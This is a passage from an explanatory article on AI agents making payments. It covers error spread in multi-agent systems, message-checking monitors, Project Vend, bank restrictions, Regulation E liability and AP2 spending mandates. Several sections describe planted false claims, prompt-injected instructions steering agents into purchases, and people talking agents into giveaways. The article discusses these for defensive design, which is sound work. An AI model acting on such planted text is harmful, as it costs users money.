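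How far an error spreads depends heavily on where it starts. In LangGraph, one of the frameworks with a central agent, a false claim from the central agent reached the whole group, while one from a worker reached 9.7% of it. In CrewAI, the figures were 100% and 15.9%. The central agent can therefore stop a worker's error or spread its own to the whole group. This complicates Kim and colleagues' case for coordinators, because a company that adds one also needs a way to check it.

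### Checking messages as they pass

Xie and colleagues' remedy is a program that intercepts every message between agents. It splits the message into separate claims and compares each one with a record of claims that it has already confirmed:

1. If the record supports the claim, the program passes it on.
2. If the record contradicts the claim, the program blocks the message and returns it to the sender with the evidence, asking for a correction.
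3. If the record settles nothing, the program either checks the claim against outside evidence or forwards it with a warning, depending on its setting.

The fast setting forwards all uncertain claims with a warning. The balanced setting checks those from influential agents, such as coordinators, and the strict setting checks every uncertain claim.

| Protection | Runs free of the planted error | Runs free of it with a usable result | Tokens per such run |
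|---|---|---|---|
| Agents review their own messages | 32% | 32% | 12,749 |
| Fast | 89% | 88% | 21,227 |
| Balanced | 93% | 91% | 30,844 |
| Strict | 94% | 93% | 57,610 |

These are averages over three frameworks and three ways of wording the false claim, and some individual results were much weaker. In LangGraph, the fast setting kept only 58% of runs clean when the claim looked like company policy. Unprotected runs in a related test used about 7,400 tokens each, so protected runs used roughly three to eight times as much computing. The strict setting also took more than three and a half minutes per successful run, compared with 41 seconds for an unprotected one.

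When the team kept the screening but removed the program's power to block or return messages, only 3.1% of runs stayed clean, almost the same as with no protection. In the invoice workflow, a checker that can only write "amount looks high" is of little use, because the paying agent can pay anyway.

The program also needs reliable information to check claims against. The researchers built their own knowledge base for these tests. A company could use its purchase orders, and an order for $1,480 would contradict the misread invoice. Without an order, the program would treat $7,480 as an uncertain claim, and the fast setting would forward it with a warning that the paying agent might ignore.

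### From one agent's response to the whole system

Yu and colleagues designed REPA to predict how badly an error would affect a system without testing every possible error from start to finish. Researchers run the same question twice, once normally and once with a false statement added. Another language model scores how much each agent's input and output changed between the runs, with separate scores for factual errors, invented content, unfaithfulness to sources and irrelevance.

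REPA uses these scores to estimate how strongly each agent's input reflects the messages it receives, and how much of an error in that input carries over into its output. It then combines the estimates along the path that messages take. With only one type of error and a one-way chain, this means multiplying them. If the checking agent passes on 30% of an error and the paying agent passes on all of what it receives, the final error is 30% of the original. But if the paying agent also reads the first agent's message and gives both messages equal weight, the final error is 65% of the original ((0.3 + 1) ÷ 2). The checker then removes only 35% of the error instead of 70%, which is a good reason to let the paying agent see only checked values.

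Yu and colleagues tested REPA's predictions on questions they had not used for fitting. The rank correlation between predicted and measured effects averaged 0.84, compared with 0.47 for a regression that linked the planted error directly to the final answer. REPA is therefore good at ranking set-ups by vulnerability but less good at predicting the size of the effect. Its average error was 0.22 to 0.24 on a scale from 0 to 1, only slightly better than the regression's 0.25 to 0.26.

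The method can also suggest where to make a repair. In another test, disabling some agents' instructions reduced accuracy to about 17%. Restoring the instructions of the one agent REPA identified raised it to 31%, close to the undamaged system's 32%. These tests involved answering questions, though, and the predictions concern how much an answer changes after a planted error, not how often a task fails. A small change in text can still be a serious financial error, since an agent that pays $7,480 instead of $1,480 has changed one character but overpaid by $6,000.

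### A manager and a shopkeeper built on the same model

Anthropic has tested having one agent manage another, with real customers and money. In the first phase, an agent called Claudius ran a small shop in the company's San Francisco office and lost money, partly because staff talked it into discounts and free items. Anthropic's *Project Vend* (2025) describes the second phase, in which Claudius got newer models, better tools and a manager, an agent called Seymour Cash. The manager set sales targets and told Claudius that all financial decisions needed its approval.

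After Cash arrived, discounts fell by about 80% and Claudius gave away half as many items. Cash also refused more than a hundred requests for lenient treatment of customers, but it approved about eight times as many, which implies more than 800 approvals. Refunds tripled and store credits doubled, and both cost the shop the full revenue from a sale, so counting only discounts would have made Cash look like a successful manager.

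As with the 93% approval rate for Claude Code's prompts, a high rate doesn't prove that the approvals were wrong, since some customers may have deserved refunds. But Anthropic, which knew the rest of the business, concluded that the shop may have started making money in spite of the manager. It notes that Cash and Claudius ran on the same underlying model and had many of the same blind spots.

In one case, an employee asked Claudius to agree in advance on a price for a large quantity of onions in January. Neither Claudius nor the second agent, Cash, saw a problem, and Cash called the idea brilliant. Cash cancelled the plan after another employee pointed out that a 1958 US law bans onion futures. Both agents seem to have made the same mistake, since neither had considered the law, so Cash's approval added confidence in the plan without making it any safer.

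Anthropic found that required procedures helped more than the manager agent did. Claudius had to look up prices and delivery times with its research tools before quoting on a new product. Its quotes then had higher prices and longer waits, but they were more realistic. Claudius could also see what the shop had paid for each item, which made it less likely to sell at a loss, and it could collect payment before placing an order. A third agent, which designed and ordered custom merchandise, was more useful than the manager, partly because its job was clearly separate from Claudius's.

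No one can tell from the experiment how much each change contributed, because Anthropic changed the models, tools and instructions over the same period, and its employees were growing tired of pressing for deals. But a price lookup might help more than a manager, because agents running on the same model tend to share errors. A supplier's website gives the agent information from outside the model, whereas Cash mostly offered a second opinion from the same one. Even in the second phase, Anthropic did not give Claudius access to a payment interface, so that it would always have to check with a person before buying anything.

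## Banks, customers and the question of who authorised a payment

Anthropic could keep Claudius away from payments because it controlled both the agent and the shop. A bank does not control an agent that logs in with a customer's password. In October and November 2026, several large US banks tried to block these agents, hold customers responsible for what the agents do, or both.

### What each bank did

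On 13 October, JPMorgan Chase's chief executive, Jamie Dimon, told investors that the bank would not let outside agents such as Muse act inside customers' accounts. "You don't want rogue agents, and there could be thousands of them," he said, according to Business Today's *US banks clamp down on transactional AI tools*. Other banks soon announced measures of their own, which fall into three groups:

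- Blocking: the bank refuses logins or transfers that it attributes to an outside agent.
- Read-only access: the agent gets account data through an approved connection, such as Plaid's.
- Contract terms: the bank treats whatever the agent does as the customer's own act.

The table combines a legal update in the National Law Review with later reports from IBTimes UK (*US Banks Block AI Agents From Customer Accounts*), Realtid (*Bankerna*) and EURweb (*Major Banks Warn About AI Access to Customer Accounts*).

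| Bank | Dates in 2026 | Does it keep agents from acting? | Read-only access | Does the customer bear the risk? |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| JPMorgan Chase | Statement 13 October, new terms 27 October | Yes | Yes, through providers such as Plaid | Yes |
| Bank of America | Interview 14 October, warning 27 October | Restricts them | Not specified | Warns that customers may be responsible |
| Charles Schwab | Statement 16 October | Blocks unauthorised agents that try to move money | In development | No new terms reported |
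| Citi | Statement 16 October, new terms in mid-November | Yes | Limited, through approved providers | Yes |
| Morgan Stanley | Reports on 22 October | Yes | Not specified | No new terms reported |
| PNC | New terms in mid-November, in force from December | Yes, unless the bank permits the agent | Not specified | Yes |
| Wells Fargo | New terms in force from 24 November | No, but it may block particular agents | Yes | Yes |

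JPMorgan forbids third parties to log in with a customer's credentials, but if a customer lets an agent in anyway, under its customer agreement the bank will rely on the agent's instructions as if they were the customer's own. The agreement takes effect on 1 January 2027, according to the National Law Review. Wells Fargo has no general ban, but it may treat requests from an outside AI tool as if they came directly from the customer, according to its *We Are Updating Our Online Access Agreement* (2026).

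Bank of America's chief executive, Brian Moynihan, said the bank was working with AI companies to ensure that a person authorises any money leaving an account. Before Morgan Stanley blocked AI agents, it had announced a plan to let clients' agents read information about employee share schemes, according to The American Bazaar. The block and the plan are compatible if the bank objects only to agents logging in as customers.

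### What the banks have seen

On 22 October, Axios reported that banks had found agents in customers' accounts that seemed to act beyond their users' instructions, and that some of these agents had contacted call centres. It cited unnamed people familiar with the matter. Mint notes that the report did not establish any financial losses. A Morgan Stanley spokesperson told Axios that the bank had seen no rogue agents on its platforms.

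Banks also struggle to tell whether an agent has exceeded its instructions, because they don't see what the customer asked for. If a customer tells an agent to keep no more than $5,000 in a current account, a transfer three weeks later may look unprompted to the bank. A phone call from an agent is just as ambiguous, because the customer may have asked for it. Muse already phones companies for its users.

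The only count of blocked agents comes from Schwab, whose chief executive, Rick Wurster, said that 10 to 20 times a week the firm blocks an unauthorised agent trying to move a client's money. He said this number was not high. The count shows that agents attempt transfers, but not whether clients had requested them, and it leaves out any agent that Schwab mistook for a client.

David Sacks, a technology investor, argued that most of the activity Axios described was customers sharing their passwords, which may break a bank's terms but is not a cyberattack. The Blaze's *Banks warn customers* (2026) quotes him, but also mentions an Axios reporter's statement that some agents appeared to have entered accounts without permission. Neither side has published data. There is much better evidence that customers share passwords than that many agents are going rogue.

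Few people may be using agents so far. Sucharita Kodali, an analyst at the research firm Forrester, says that most people don't know what agents are, but she thinks it is reasonable for banks to act now.

### What a password proves

When a customer logs in, the bank checks a username, a password and often a one-time code sent to the customer's phone. The code is supposed to show that whoever is logging in has the phone. But a customer who wants an agent to pay bills will give it the code, so the code shows only that the customer cooperated at some point. American Banker's *Banks aren't ready for AI agents moving money, experts warn* describes how banks built their defences for people, not for software using a customer's own credentials.

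After login, the bank's records do not show whether the customer or the agent made a payment. The customer can end the agent's access only by changing the password.

Banks already have a better arrangement for human helpers. Under Wells Fargo's *Online Access Agreement* (May 2026), an account owner can appoint a delegate, such as a bookkeeper, who has a separate username and password. The owner can limit what the delegate may do, in some cases to viewing the account. The bank can therefore tell the delegate from the owner, and can end the delegate's access without locking out the owner.

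Suppose an agent uses the customer's password to send $2,000 to a new payee. Deciding what to do about the payment involves four questions that are easy to confuse.

| Question | What would answer it | Does the bank have this? |
|---|---|---|
| Is this an agent? | A signal from the software, or behaviour unlike a person's | Sometimes |
| Is the login valid? | The username, password and code | Yes |
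| Did the customer allow this payment? | What the customer told the agent | No, the customer and the AI company have it |
| Who answers for a loss? | The law and the contracts | Only in part, because the law may depend on what the customer allowed |

Meta is developing a protocol called Poppy that would let companies know when a personal agent is acting for a customer. This would help them recognise legitimate agents, but criminals would have no reason to make their software identify itself. Knowing that Muse sent a payment also doesn't show that its user wanted it. PYMNTS's *Regulators Converge on Twin Compliance Challenges From AI Agents* (2026) reports that financial officials speaking on 16 November discussed how institutions can determine whether a customer's agent has authority to move money.

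The banks' new terms avoid the difficulty by making the customer liable for any payment made with a valid login, whatever the customer had allowed. Whether the banks can do this depends mainly on federal law.

### When a transfer is unauthorised

Regulation E implements the Electronic Fund Transfer Act, the US law that protects consumers when money moves electronically into or out of their bank accounts. Bankrate's *What is Regulation E?* (2025) explains that it covers debit cards, online transfers and payment services such as Zelle, but not credit cards or wire transfers. A customer's loss from an unauthorised transfer is limited to $50 if they report it within two business days, or $500 if they report it within 60 days. The bank has 10 business days to investigate, and must credit the account provisionally if it needs longer.

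Section 1005.2(m) of the regulation sets three conditions for an unauthorised transfer:

- Someone other than the consumer initiates it.
- That person has no actual authority to initiate it.
- The consumer receives no benefit from it.

However, a transfer does not count as unauthorised if the consumer gave the "access device" to the person who made it, unless the consumer had already told the bank that this person's transfers were no longer authorised. An access device is a card, code or other means of access to the account, such as a username and password. Under the official commentary, consumers who hand over an access device are fully liable even if the recipient exceeds the authority they gave. For example, someone who lends a friend a debit card to withdraw $50 cannot recover the other $450 from the bank if the friend takes $500.

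The commentary gives family members and co-workers as examples, and the definition doesn't mention software. In the regulation, a "person" is a human being or an organisation, so an AI agent isn't one. This gap probably helps the bank, because the transfer is not unauthorised on either reading of who initiated it. If the agent is the customer's tool, the customer initiated the transfer. If the company running the agent initiated it, the customer had given that company the password.

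### Three ways to lose $2,000

Suppose a customer gives an agent their bank password, $2,000 leaves the account by an ordinary online transfer, and the customer reports it the next morning. How much the customer loses depends on what went wrong.

| What happened | Likely position under Regulation E | Customer's loss |
|---|---|---|
| The agent misread an instruction | Not unauthorised | $2,000 |
| A stranger steered the agent | Disputable | $50 or $2,000 |
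| A thief stole the password from the agent's provider | Unauthorised | $50 |

If the agent misread an instruction, for example by paying a deposit twice, the rule about exceeding authority fits closely. The customer can ask the payee to return the money, but probably has no claim against the bank. Engadget's *Unauthorized AI agents are reportedly already accessing US bank accounts* goes further, saying that banks wouldn't be liable when an agent does something wrong, because the customer gave it access to the account. That is probably right about the agent's own mistakes but too broad for payments involving a criminal.

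If a criminal planted an instruction that made the agent transfer money, the bank can argue that the agent used a password the customer had supplied. The customer can reply that the criminal made the transfer, using the agent as an instrument, and that nobody had given the criminal access.

Each side has an analogy in existing practice. Bankrate says Regulation E may not help when a criminal tricks a customer into sending a payment, because the customer did authorise the transaction. But the regulation's official commentary treats a transfer as unauthorised if a criminal made it with an access device obtained through fraud. Bankrate adds that the Consumer Financial Protection Bureau (CFPB), the agency responsible for the regulation, confirmed in January 2025 that customers keep their protection when someone tricks them into revealing their login.

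How an attacker steers the agent might therefore affect whether a payment counts as authorised. A forged gas bill leads the agent to make the kind of payment its user requested, much as a forged invoice fools a person. A planted instruction to empty a savings account has little to do with the user's request and looks more like someone taking over the account.

*BofA Ruling Opens Door To EFTA Online Wire Fraud Claims* (Dryhurst and Mezzino, 2026) describes such a takeover without an AI agent. A caller posing as bank staff gained control of a Bank of America customer's phone and moved $106,000 to another bank. The customer reported it within minutes, but Bank of America denied the claims, saying the transfers were wires, which it considered outside the federal law. As the title indicates, a ruling may now make it easier to bring such claims over online wires. Without such a ruling, a customer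 whose agent can send wires may have much less protection than one whose agent can only make ordinary transfers.

The customer's case is strongest if a thief stole the password from the AI company. The thief had no authority, and the customer never gave the thief the password. Sharing it with the company may have been careless, but the official commentary does not let banks make customers bear more of the loss because of negligence, even if a customer wrote a PIN on the card. The Act also requires the bank to prove that a disputed transfer was authorised.

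The customer could still have trouble proving that a thief made the transfer. Either the thief or the agent would have logged in with the right password, and the bank could argue that the agent was the more likely explanation. The customer might then need the AI company's logs to show that the agent had not made the transfer.

### How far a contract can go

According to Realtid, which relays TechCrunch's reporting, Citi's new terms make customers bear the loss even if the AI tool leaks their login or someone hacks it. TechRadar's *Major US banks crack down on AI agent use by customers* also describes customers as fully at fault if there is a hack. This part of the new terms conflicts most directly with Regulation E. A contract cannot waive consumers' rights under the Electronic Fund Transfer Act, so a bank probably can't use such a clause to make a theft victim pay more than the legal limits.

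The clauses can still matter, because customers who believe them may never dispute a payment. They matter more for business accounts, which Regulation E does not protect, so a company that lets an agent pay its suppliers has more reason than a household to read them carefully. The Act's ban on waivers also doesn't oblige a bank to give agents access to accounts. Wells Fargo's earlier terms for human delegates already made customers solely responsible for transactions they "did not want or intend", but added "unless prohibited by applicable law".

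Hill (2026) reports that financial services attorneys see the use of AI agents as a possible test of consumer protection law and a source of litigation. According to the National Law Review, regulators have privately welcomed the banks' restrictions but have indicated that the law on authorisation and liability may need clarifying.

Banks and customers are likely to dispute how a customer ends an agent's authority. Wells Fargo's new terms require customers to revoke the agent's access in time, keep evidence of this and show it to the bank on request. Realtid quotes Elaine Duffus, a consultant at Wolters Kluwer, who asks what happens if the customer can prove they revoked access in time but the agent keeps acting anyway. Under Regulation E, telling the bank should be enough to make later transfers unauthorised, and the regulation doesn't mention proof that the customer also told the AI company.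 This is difficult for the bank, because customers can grant and revoke an agent's access outside the bank's systems. A customer who has shared a password should notify the bank and change the password on the same day.

The AI company could also bear the loss. But Meta's terms hold users responsible for what Muse does, so a Citi customer who uses Muse has two contracts that assign the loss to the customer. At a banking conference in November, a New York enforcement attorney argued that AI providers should pay when their software exceeds its instructions, according to PYMNTS's *Panel Weighs Who Pays When AI Agents Exceed Consumers’ Instructions* (2026). There is a good case for this, because the provider can correct the agent and usually has the fullest record of what the user asked for. But someone would have to decide what counts as exceeding an instruction. If a user told an agent to "pay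 this month's bills" and then disputed one of the payments, the user and the provider could both have reasonable arguments.

A customer's protection also depends on the method of payment. Credit cards fall under a separate regulation, which Bankrate says often gives customers stronger protection than Regulation E.

### Card protection in the United Kingdom

British shoppers have two well-known protections, but neither is designed for an agent's mistakes. Section 75 of the Consumer Credit Act 1974 makes a credit card company liable alongside the seller for a breach of contract or a misrepresentation, if the item costs more than £100 and no more than £30,000. Chargeback, which also covers debit cards, is a procedure under the card networks' rules that lets the customer's bank try to recover a payment from the seller's bank, for instance when goods never arrive. If an agent orders the wrong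 laptop and the shop delivers what it ordered, the shop has kept to the contract, so Section 75 does not apply and a chargeback would probably fail. The 14-day right to cancel most online purchases would be more useful, though it excludes hotel rooms booked for particular dates. UK rules on unauthorised bank payments are harsher than Regulation E on careless customers, who can lose their right to a refund if they were grossly negligent with their login.

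### Does the customer's permission bind the company?

A customer might argue that they should be able to choose who helps them use their own account. Amazon's lawsuit against the AI company Perplexity raises a similar question about shopping accounts. Perplexity's web browser, Comet, has an assistant that can log in to a user's Amazon account and place orders. Amazon sued in November 2025 under the Computer Fraud and Abuse Act, a federal law against hacking. In March 2026 a judge temporarily barred the assistant from Amazon, but on 4 August the Ninth Circuit, a federal appeals court, lifted the ban.

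The appeals court's reasoning depended on how the software works. According to Mondaq's *Ninth Circuit Vacates CFAA Injunction Against Perplexity's Comet AI Agent*, the browser runs on the user's own computer and communicates with Amazon, while the assistant sends screenshots to Perplexity's servers, which return instructions for navigating the site. Because Perplexity's servers never communicate with Amazon's, the court concluded that the user, not Perplexity, accessed Amazon's computers. Amazon had argued that Perplexity was responsible because its servers sent the assistant instructions, according to Mondaq's *Web Scraping Digest*.

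This is a narrow victory for users. The Indian Express' *Amazon loses US court ban on Perplexity’s AI shopping tools* quotes Perplexity's spokesperson on the right of internet users to choose whatever AI they want, but the court decided only whose access was at issue under the hacking law, based on the evidence before it. It did not rule that a user's permission overrides a website's refusal. Companies can still forbid agents in their terms and block them technically, as Amazon has done with Muse.

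The reasoning may also not apply to Muse, which runs on a virtual machine in Meta's cloud. If Muse logs in to a bank from there, Meta's computers communicate directly with the bank's. The ruling could even hurt a customer in a payment dispute, because a bank might argue that if the user is the one who accesses a website through an agent, the user is also the one who initiates a transfer through it. The two laws have different purposes and wording, so a court need not accept the comparison.

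The Ninth Circuit left its ruling in place on 10 September (MediaPost, *Appeals Court Again Rejects Amazon Bid To Block Perplexity*, 2026). On 1 December, a judge trimmed Amazon's amended lawsuit but allowed its claims about the assistant on iPhones and iPads to proceed (Eslinger, *Amazon's iOS Claims Against Perplexity Clear Dismissal Bid*, 2026).

### Cheap deposits and the right to data

Banks have a financial reason to keep agents from moving money. Many customers leave savings in current accounts that pay about 0.1% a year, while alternatives pay 3.3% to 5%. An agent could move the money to a better-paying account every time the balance rose, sparing customers the effort that now discourages them from doing it. Torsten Slok, chief economist at the investment firm Apollo, has warned that this could reduce the cheap deposits banks use to fund loans. The National Law Review mentions one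 estimate of the cost to banks, $47 billion a year.

A bank worried about theft and a bank worried about losing deposits would both let agents read balances but block transfers, so these measures alone don't show how much deposits matter to the banks. Better evidence would be whether banks offer agents a supervised way to make payments, and whether the banks' own assistants will move a customer's savings to a competitor that pays more. Schwab has launched an assistant called Charley, and Citi's new terms exempt its own AI tools. Supervised access seems feasible, since Robinhood, a brokerage, already offers separate accounts for agents, though customers bear the risk. Sacks wants banks to support agents that customers direct, and points to American Express, whose connection to Muse lets users limit and revoke access. He accepts read-only access as a sensible interim step.

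Customers have a stronger legal claim to their data than to having an agent act for them. Section 1033 of the Dodd-Frank Act, a US financial reform law, entitles consumers to electronic information about their own accounts. In October 2024 the CFPB issued a rule requiring banks to share this information free with third parties the customer has authorised. Mondaq's *Open Banking Regulation In 2026* explains that the rule also covered the details a third party needs to initiate a payment, but left the payment itself to other rules.

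The rule has not been repealed, but the CFPB can't enforce it. Banking groups sued, and a federal court in Kentucky found that the agency had probably exceeded its powers. The appeal is on hold while the CFPB rewrites the rule, and the first compliance date, 1 April 2026, passed without effect. In August the agency sent a new proposal to the White House for review, normally one of the last steps before publication, according to Mondaq's *CFPB Sends New Section 1033 “Open Banking” Proposal To OIRA For Review*. Such reviews ordinarily take no more than 90 days, so this one would have been due to end by late November, but the proposal doesn't seem to have been published by early December. Publication would only open a public comment period, so a final rule is probably still some way off.

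The CFPB is reconsidering two questions that directly affect agents: whether banks may charge for access, and who counts as a consumer's representative. If banks can charge AI companies a reasonable fee for a supervised connection, they will have more reason to offer one. If the CFPB defines representatives narrowly, an AI company might have no right to a customer's data even with the customer's consent, and banks could withdraw the read-only access that most now allow.

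## Payment mandates, or spending limits checked outside the agent

When an agent pays from a customer's account, the bank can check the password but has no record of what the customer allowed. A payment mandate is a machine-readable record of that permission. The customer sets limits once and signs them, and the shop or the bank checks each payment against them. An agent that has misread its instructions or obeyed a stranger's email can still request a payment outside the limits, but ordinary software should refuse it.

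A digital signature is a number that a device computes from a document and a secret key. Anyone with the matching public key can check that the holder of the secret key signed exactly that text. Changing a single digit makes the check fail, so an agent can't change a signed limit of £150 to £1,500 without being detected.

### What AP2 asks each company to check

Google announced the Agent Payments Protocol (AP2) in September 2025. More than 60 firms supported the launch, including American Express, Mastercard and PayPal, according to PYMNTS's *Google Unveils a Payment Protocol for AI-Driven Commerce*. Google has since donated AP2 to the FIDO Alliance, an industry group that develops login standards. The latest version appears to be 0.2. Companies that supported the launch may not accept AP2 payments today, and there seem to be no public figures on how many purchases use AP2.

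AP2's *Agentic Payment Protocol (v0.2)* defines two kinds of mandate:

| Mandate | What it can limit | Who checks it |
|---|---|---|
| Checkout mandate | The shop, the items and the quantity | The shop |
| Payment mandate | The amount, the payee, the means of payment and the payment date | The wallet company or other firm that supplies the payment details, the card network if there is one, and the shop's payment processor |

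These checks must run in ordinary code, even if a company uses a language model for other work. The screen where the user approves a mandate can't depend on a language model either.

If the user is present, the agent fills a basket and the shop signs it to confirm the items and the price. The user then sees the final purchase, approves it (with a fingerprint, for example) and signs both mandates. According to the specification, a normal online checkout would often work just as well in this case.

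If the user will be away, they sign "open" mandates in advance, which contain the limits and the agent's public key. When the agent finds something to buy, it signs "closed" mandates for that purchase and sends both sets. The companies check both signatures and check that the purchase is within the limits. A thief who copied the open mandates couldn't use them without the agent's secret key.

AP2's *Agent Payments Protocol Documentation* assumes that nobody can reliably prevent prompt injection and treats every agent as a potential attacker. AP2 checks only the resulting purchase, without trying to make the agent trustworthy, whereas CaMeL tracks untrusted text inside the agent.

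### Running shoes, up to £150, by Friday

Suppose a user types "running shoes, up to £150, by Friday" on Monday and goes to work:

1. The agent turns the request into limits. AP2 has no limit for a category such as running shoes, so the agent lists the item codes of three suitable pairs and the two shops that sell them. It sets the maximum at 15,000 pence and the last payment date at Friday.
2. The user's wallet app displays the limits. The user approves them, and the app signs the open mandates.
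3. On Wednesday, one pair drops to £139. The shop signs a checkout with the item and the price, and the agent signs the closed mandates.
4. The wallet company checks the amount, payee and date, and releases a payment token for this purchase.
5. The shop checks that it is on the list and that the shoes are too. Its payment processor confirms that the token belongs to this checkout and takes the £139.
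6. The shop and the processor return signed receipts.

The limits stop some failures and let others through.

| What goes wrong | Do the limits stop it? |
|---|---|
| The price rises to £165 | Yes |
| The agent tries to pay on Saturday | Yes |
| The agent pays on Thursday, but the shoes arrive the following Tuesday | No |
| The agent buys a £60 kettle | Only if the mandate lists items |
| The shoes are the wrong size | Only if the item codes specify the right size |
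| The shop has a terrible reputation | Only if the mandate lists shops and leaves this one out |
| Planted text steers the agent to a worse pair at £149 | Only if the mandate leaves that pair or its shop out |

"By Friday" probably means the user wants the shoes by then, but AP2 can limit only the payment date. Developers can define new limits, including one for delivery, but a company whose software doesn't recognise a limit must treat the purchase as failing it. A delivery limit would therefore be useful only at shops that had adopted it.

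A sample mandate in AP2's documentation includes an item code for a women's size 9 shoe, and a shop checking that code would refuse to sell a size 8. But the agent chooses the code, so if it picks the wrong size and the user doesn't notice on the approval screen, the wrong shoes will pass every later check.

Ordinary code can also enforce the wrong limit if companies read the amount in different units. The documentation defines the maximum payment in cents or pence, but one of its examples gives "100.50", which looks like dollars. If one company's software wrote 15,000 for £150 and another's read the number as pounds, the cap would be £15,000. The companies would need to test for this before relying on the limit.

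A purchase steered by planted text is the hardest case, because it can satisfy every limit. AP2's designers accept that an agent misled this way may choose badly, but argue that the limits cap the harm. If the £149 shoes are worth £60, the user has overpaid by £89. If the mandate names no shops and the seller is a fraud, the user could lose the full £149, but not the rest of the account.

### How caps bound the loss

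As with Lobstar Wilde's transfers, a cap on each payment needs a cap on the total to go with it. A £50 cap alone would let an agent spend £1,000 on 20 bad payments overnight, but a monthly cap of £150 would stop it after the third. With a cap of c per payment and B per month, n bad payments in a month can cost at most

min(n × c, B).

The £150 cap applies to each mandate separately and resets every calendar month. A fraud that starts on 31 May and continues on 1 June can therefore take £300. Ten mandates with different shops, each capped at £150, put up to £1,500 a month at risk.

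In the earlier example, an agent pays eight monthly bills totaling $1,200 from a login that can also reach $40,000 in savings. Caps of $250 per payment and $1,400 per month would limit the most it could lose in a month to $1,400, instead of the whole balance. Fraud that occurs after the agent has paid the bills could take only the remaining $200. If the fraud comes first, it could use up the allowance, so the bank would refuse the real bills and the user might owe late fees.

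The caps would also block a correct gas bill of $260 in a cold January. The user could raise the cap, but that would increase the possible loss every month. Approving the occasional large bill by hand is probably better.

Enforcing a monthly cap requires a running total of spending. A shop knows only its own sales, so the bank or wallet company has to keep the total. AP2 has a budget limit, but it covers the whole life of a mandate instead of resetting each month. A user could get a monthly cap by allowing one payment a month and limiting its size.

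Even the shoe mandate needs this kind of record. AP2 forbids an agent from using the same mandate for a second purchase unless it has received a rejection for the first. Wallet companies and card networks may reject duplicates, but AP2 doesn't require them to. If the agent broke the rule and no company rejected the second purchase, a £150 mandate could pay for two pairs of shoes.

### Nine pizzas from a bank account

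In November 2026, an AI agent run by the pizza chain Papa John's paid for nine mini margheritas directly from a customer's bank account. The payment was part of a trial in a regulatory sandbox run by Britain's Financial Conduct Authority (FCA), where firms test new financial products under supervision and with limited exposure. Lloyds was the bank, and TrueLayer, which connects shops to bank accounts, arranged the payment.

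The trial used variable recurring payments, which Tech.eu's *Papa John’s pizza order first UK cardless payment by AI agent* (2026) describes as permission for a payment provider to take repeated payments of varying amounts. The customer creates the mandate once, in the bank's own app, and chooses the limits there. This trial had a limit for each transaction and another for the month. The bank checks every payment against the limits and declines any that goes over. According to The Paypers' *Papa John's, TrueLayer test AI-led Pay by Bank*, the agent never receives the customer's banking password, and the customer can cancel the mandate in the app or with the shop.

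The company that holds the money also enforces the limit, which is simpler than AP2's chain of signatures. But the bank's limits cover only the shop and the amount, so an order for nine pizzas with the wrong topping at the same price would have been within them.

The pizza order is better evidence that the payment method works than that it would restrain a misbehaving agent. TechRadar's *Nine Papa John's pizzas, no credit card* reports that the customer's group confirmed the order before the agent paid, and the published accounts don't describe any attempt to exceed the limits. TrueLayer also has a commercial interest in the result, since it sells an alternative to cards. Al Bayan's *9 قطع بيتزا تدخل تاريخ الذكاء الاصطناعي* quotes its chief executive as saying that shoppers keep their buyer protection if an order goes wrong, but this can't include chargeback or Section 75, which depend on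 paying by card.

TrueLayer calls this the first time an AI agent paid a UK retailer in this way. Its claim is limited to retail payments of this kind, as the payment company GoCardless had already collected a live donation for the food bank charity Trussell in September, in a different FCA programme. GoCardless' *Five lessons from testing agentic payments with the FCA* (2026) describes a chat agent that helps a donor set up a Direct Debit, a standing permission for an organisation to collect money from a bank account.

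GoCardless kept the donor's consent and bank details away from the model. The donor enters the details in a secure form inside the chat, and the agent receives only status updates such as "payer confirmed". GoCardless says in *What we learned building the UK's first agentic bank payment* (2026) that it did this because nobody can guarantee that a model will record consent correctly every time. Employees tried to mislead the agent in almost 400 conversations, and GoCardless reports that the agent refused or returned to the subject of donations each time. This result is encouraging, but employees testing a demo have less to gain than thieves would.

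### A separate account at Robinhood

Robinhood announced its accounts for AI agents on 27 May 2026. An agent can trade only with money that the customer has moved into a separate account, according to Bloomberg's *Robinhood Launches AI Stock Trading, Purchases on Credit Cards* (2026). The Paypers' *Robinhood launches agentic trading and credit card features* adds that customers get a notification for every trade and can disconnect the agent at any time. For purchases, Robinhood offers agents virtual credit cards with spending limits. The customer can disable a card instantly or set it to require manual approval.

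The separate account caps losses without requiring any interpretation. If a customer deposits $1,000 and the agent can spend only that money, it can lose at most $1,000, but the cap doesn't prevent it from losing the full amount. A shop's software can check a pair of shoes against a list, but no simple rule can distinguish a bad investment from a good one that hasn't paid off yet. The Information points out that it may be too early to judge how well agents trade.

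The cut-off switch helps only once the customer notices a problem. An agent that makes a poor trade every minute can make 480 while the customer sleeps for eight hours, and the notifications won't help until morning. The deposit limits the customer's losses in the meantime, as long as they don't keep topping it up.

Robinhood has also expanded what agents can trade from shares to options and cryptocurrency, though they can't transfer crypto out of the account, according to Finder. That restriction would have prevented a loss like Lobstar Wilde's. Robinhood doesn't supervise or audit the agents customers connect and leaves customers responsible for monitoring them, according to Pulse 2.0's *Robinhood Launches Agentic Trading And AI Credit Card*.

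### A purchase without a mandate

A mandate protects the user only if the agent can't pay another way. *Google can track exactly how your agent spends your money* (Luitel, Fortune, August 2026) gives the example of a user who tells an agent to find a shirt for less than $30 but not to buy it. The agent orders one anyway. The shop accepts the order because the user connected it to the agent weeks earlier, so the access token is valid. The shop doesn't receive the instruction not to buy, which stays with the AI company.

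If the shop had required an AP2 mandate, the agent would have had none to present, because the user had not approved any purchase. But a shop that doesn't support mandates may still accept a saved card, and an agent may find another credential, as the agent at PocketOS did. For a mandate to limit the agent, users also have to remove saved cards and shared passwords.

The shop also has to know it's dealing with an agent before it can ask for a mandate. Only 23% of merchants can clearly identify AI traffic, according to PYMNTS's *Meta and Sierra’s Poppy Lets Customers Set Limits for AI Agents*.

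Poppy is a protocol that Meta is developing with the customer service company Sierra. A business uses it to publish the addresses that agents should use, verify which agent is calling, and open a session that only this agent can use, according to Help Net Security's *Descope Envoy brings AI agent authentication to consumer apps* (2026). The agent starts as a guest, which is enough to check whether something is in stock. For anything involving an account, the customer signs in and chooses read-only or write access. Sierra's *Bret Taylor* lists the release of version 1.0 on 13 November 2026, for everyone who uses Muse and every merchant on Shopify.

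Write access could be as broad as the permission that Matt Robb gave Muse. Someone who grants write access so that an agent can change a delivery address may not expect it to cancel the order. In October, limits on specific actions and support for payments were still only possible additions to Poppy, according to The Paypers' *Meta and Sierra develop AI agent protocol*. Poppy and AP2 could therefore complement each other, with Poppy identifying the agent and AP2 specifying what it may buy.

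### Connecting the records

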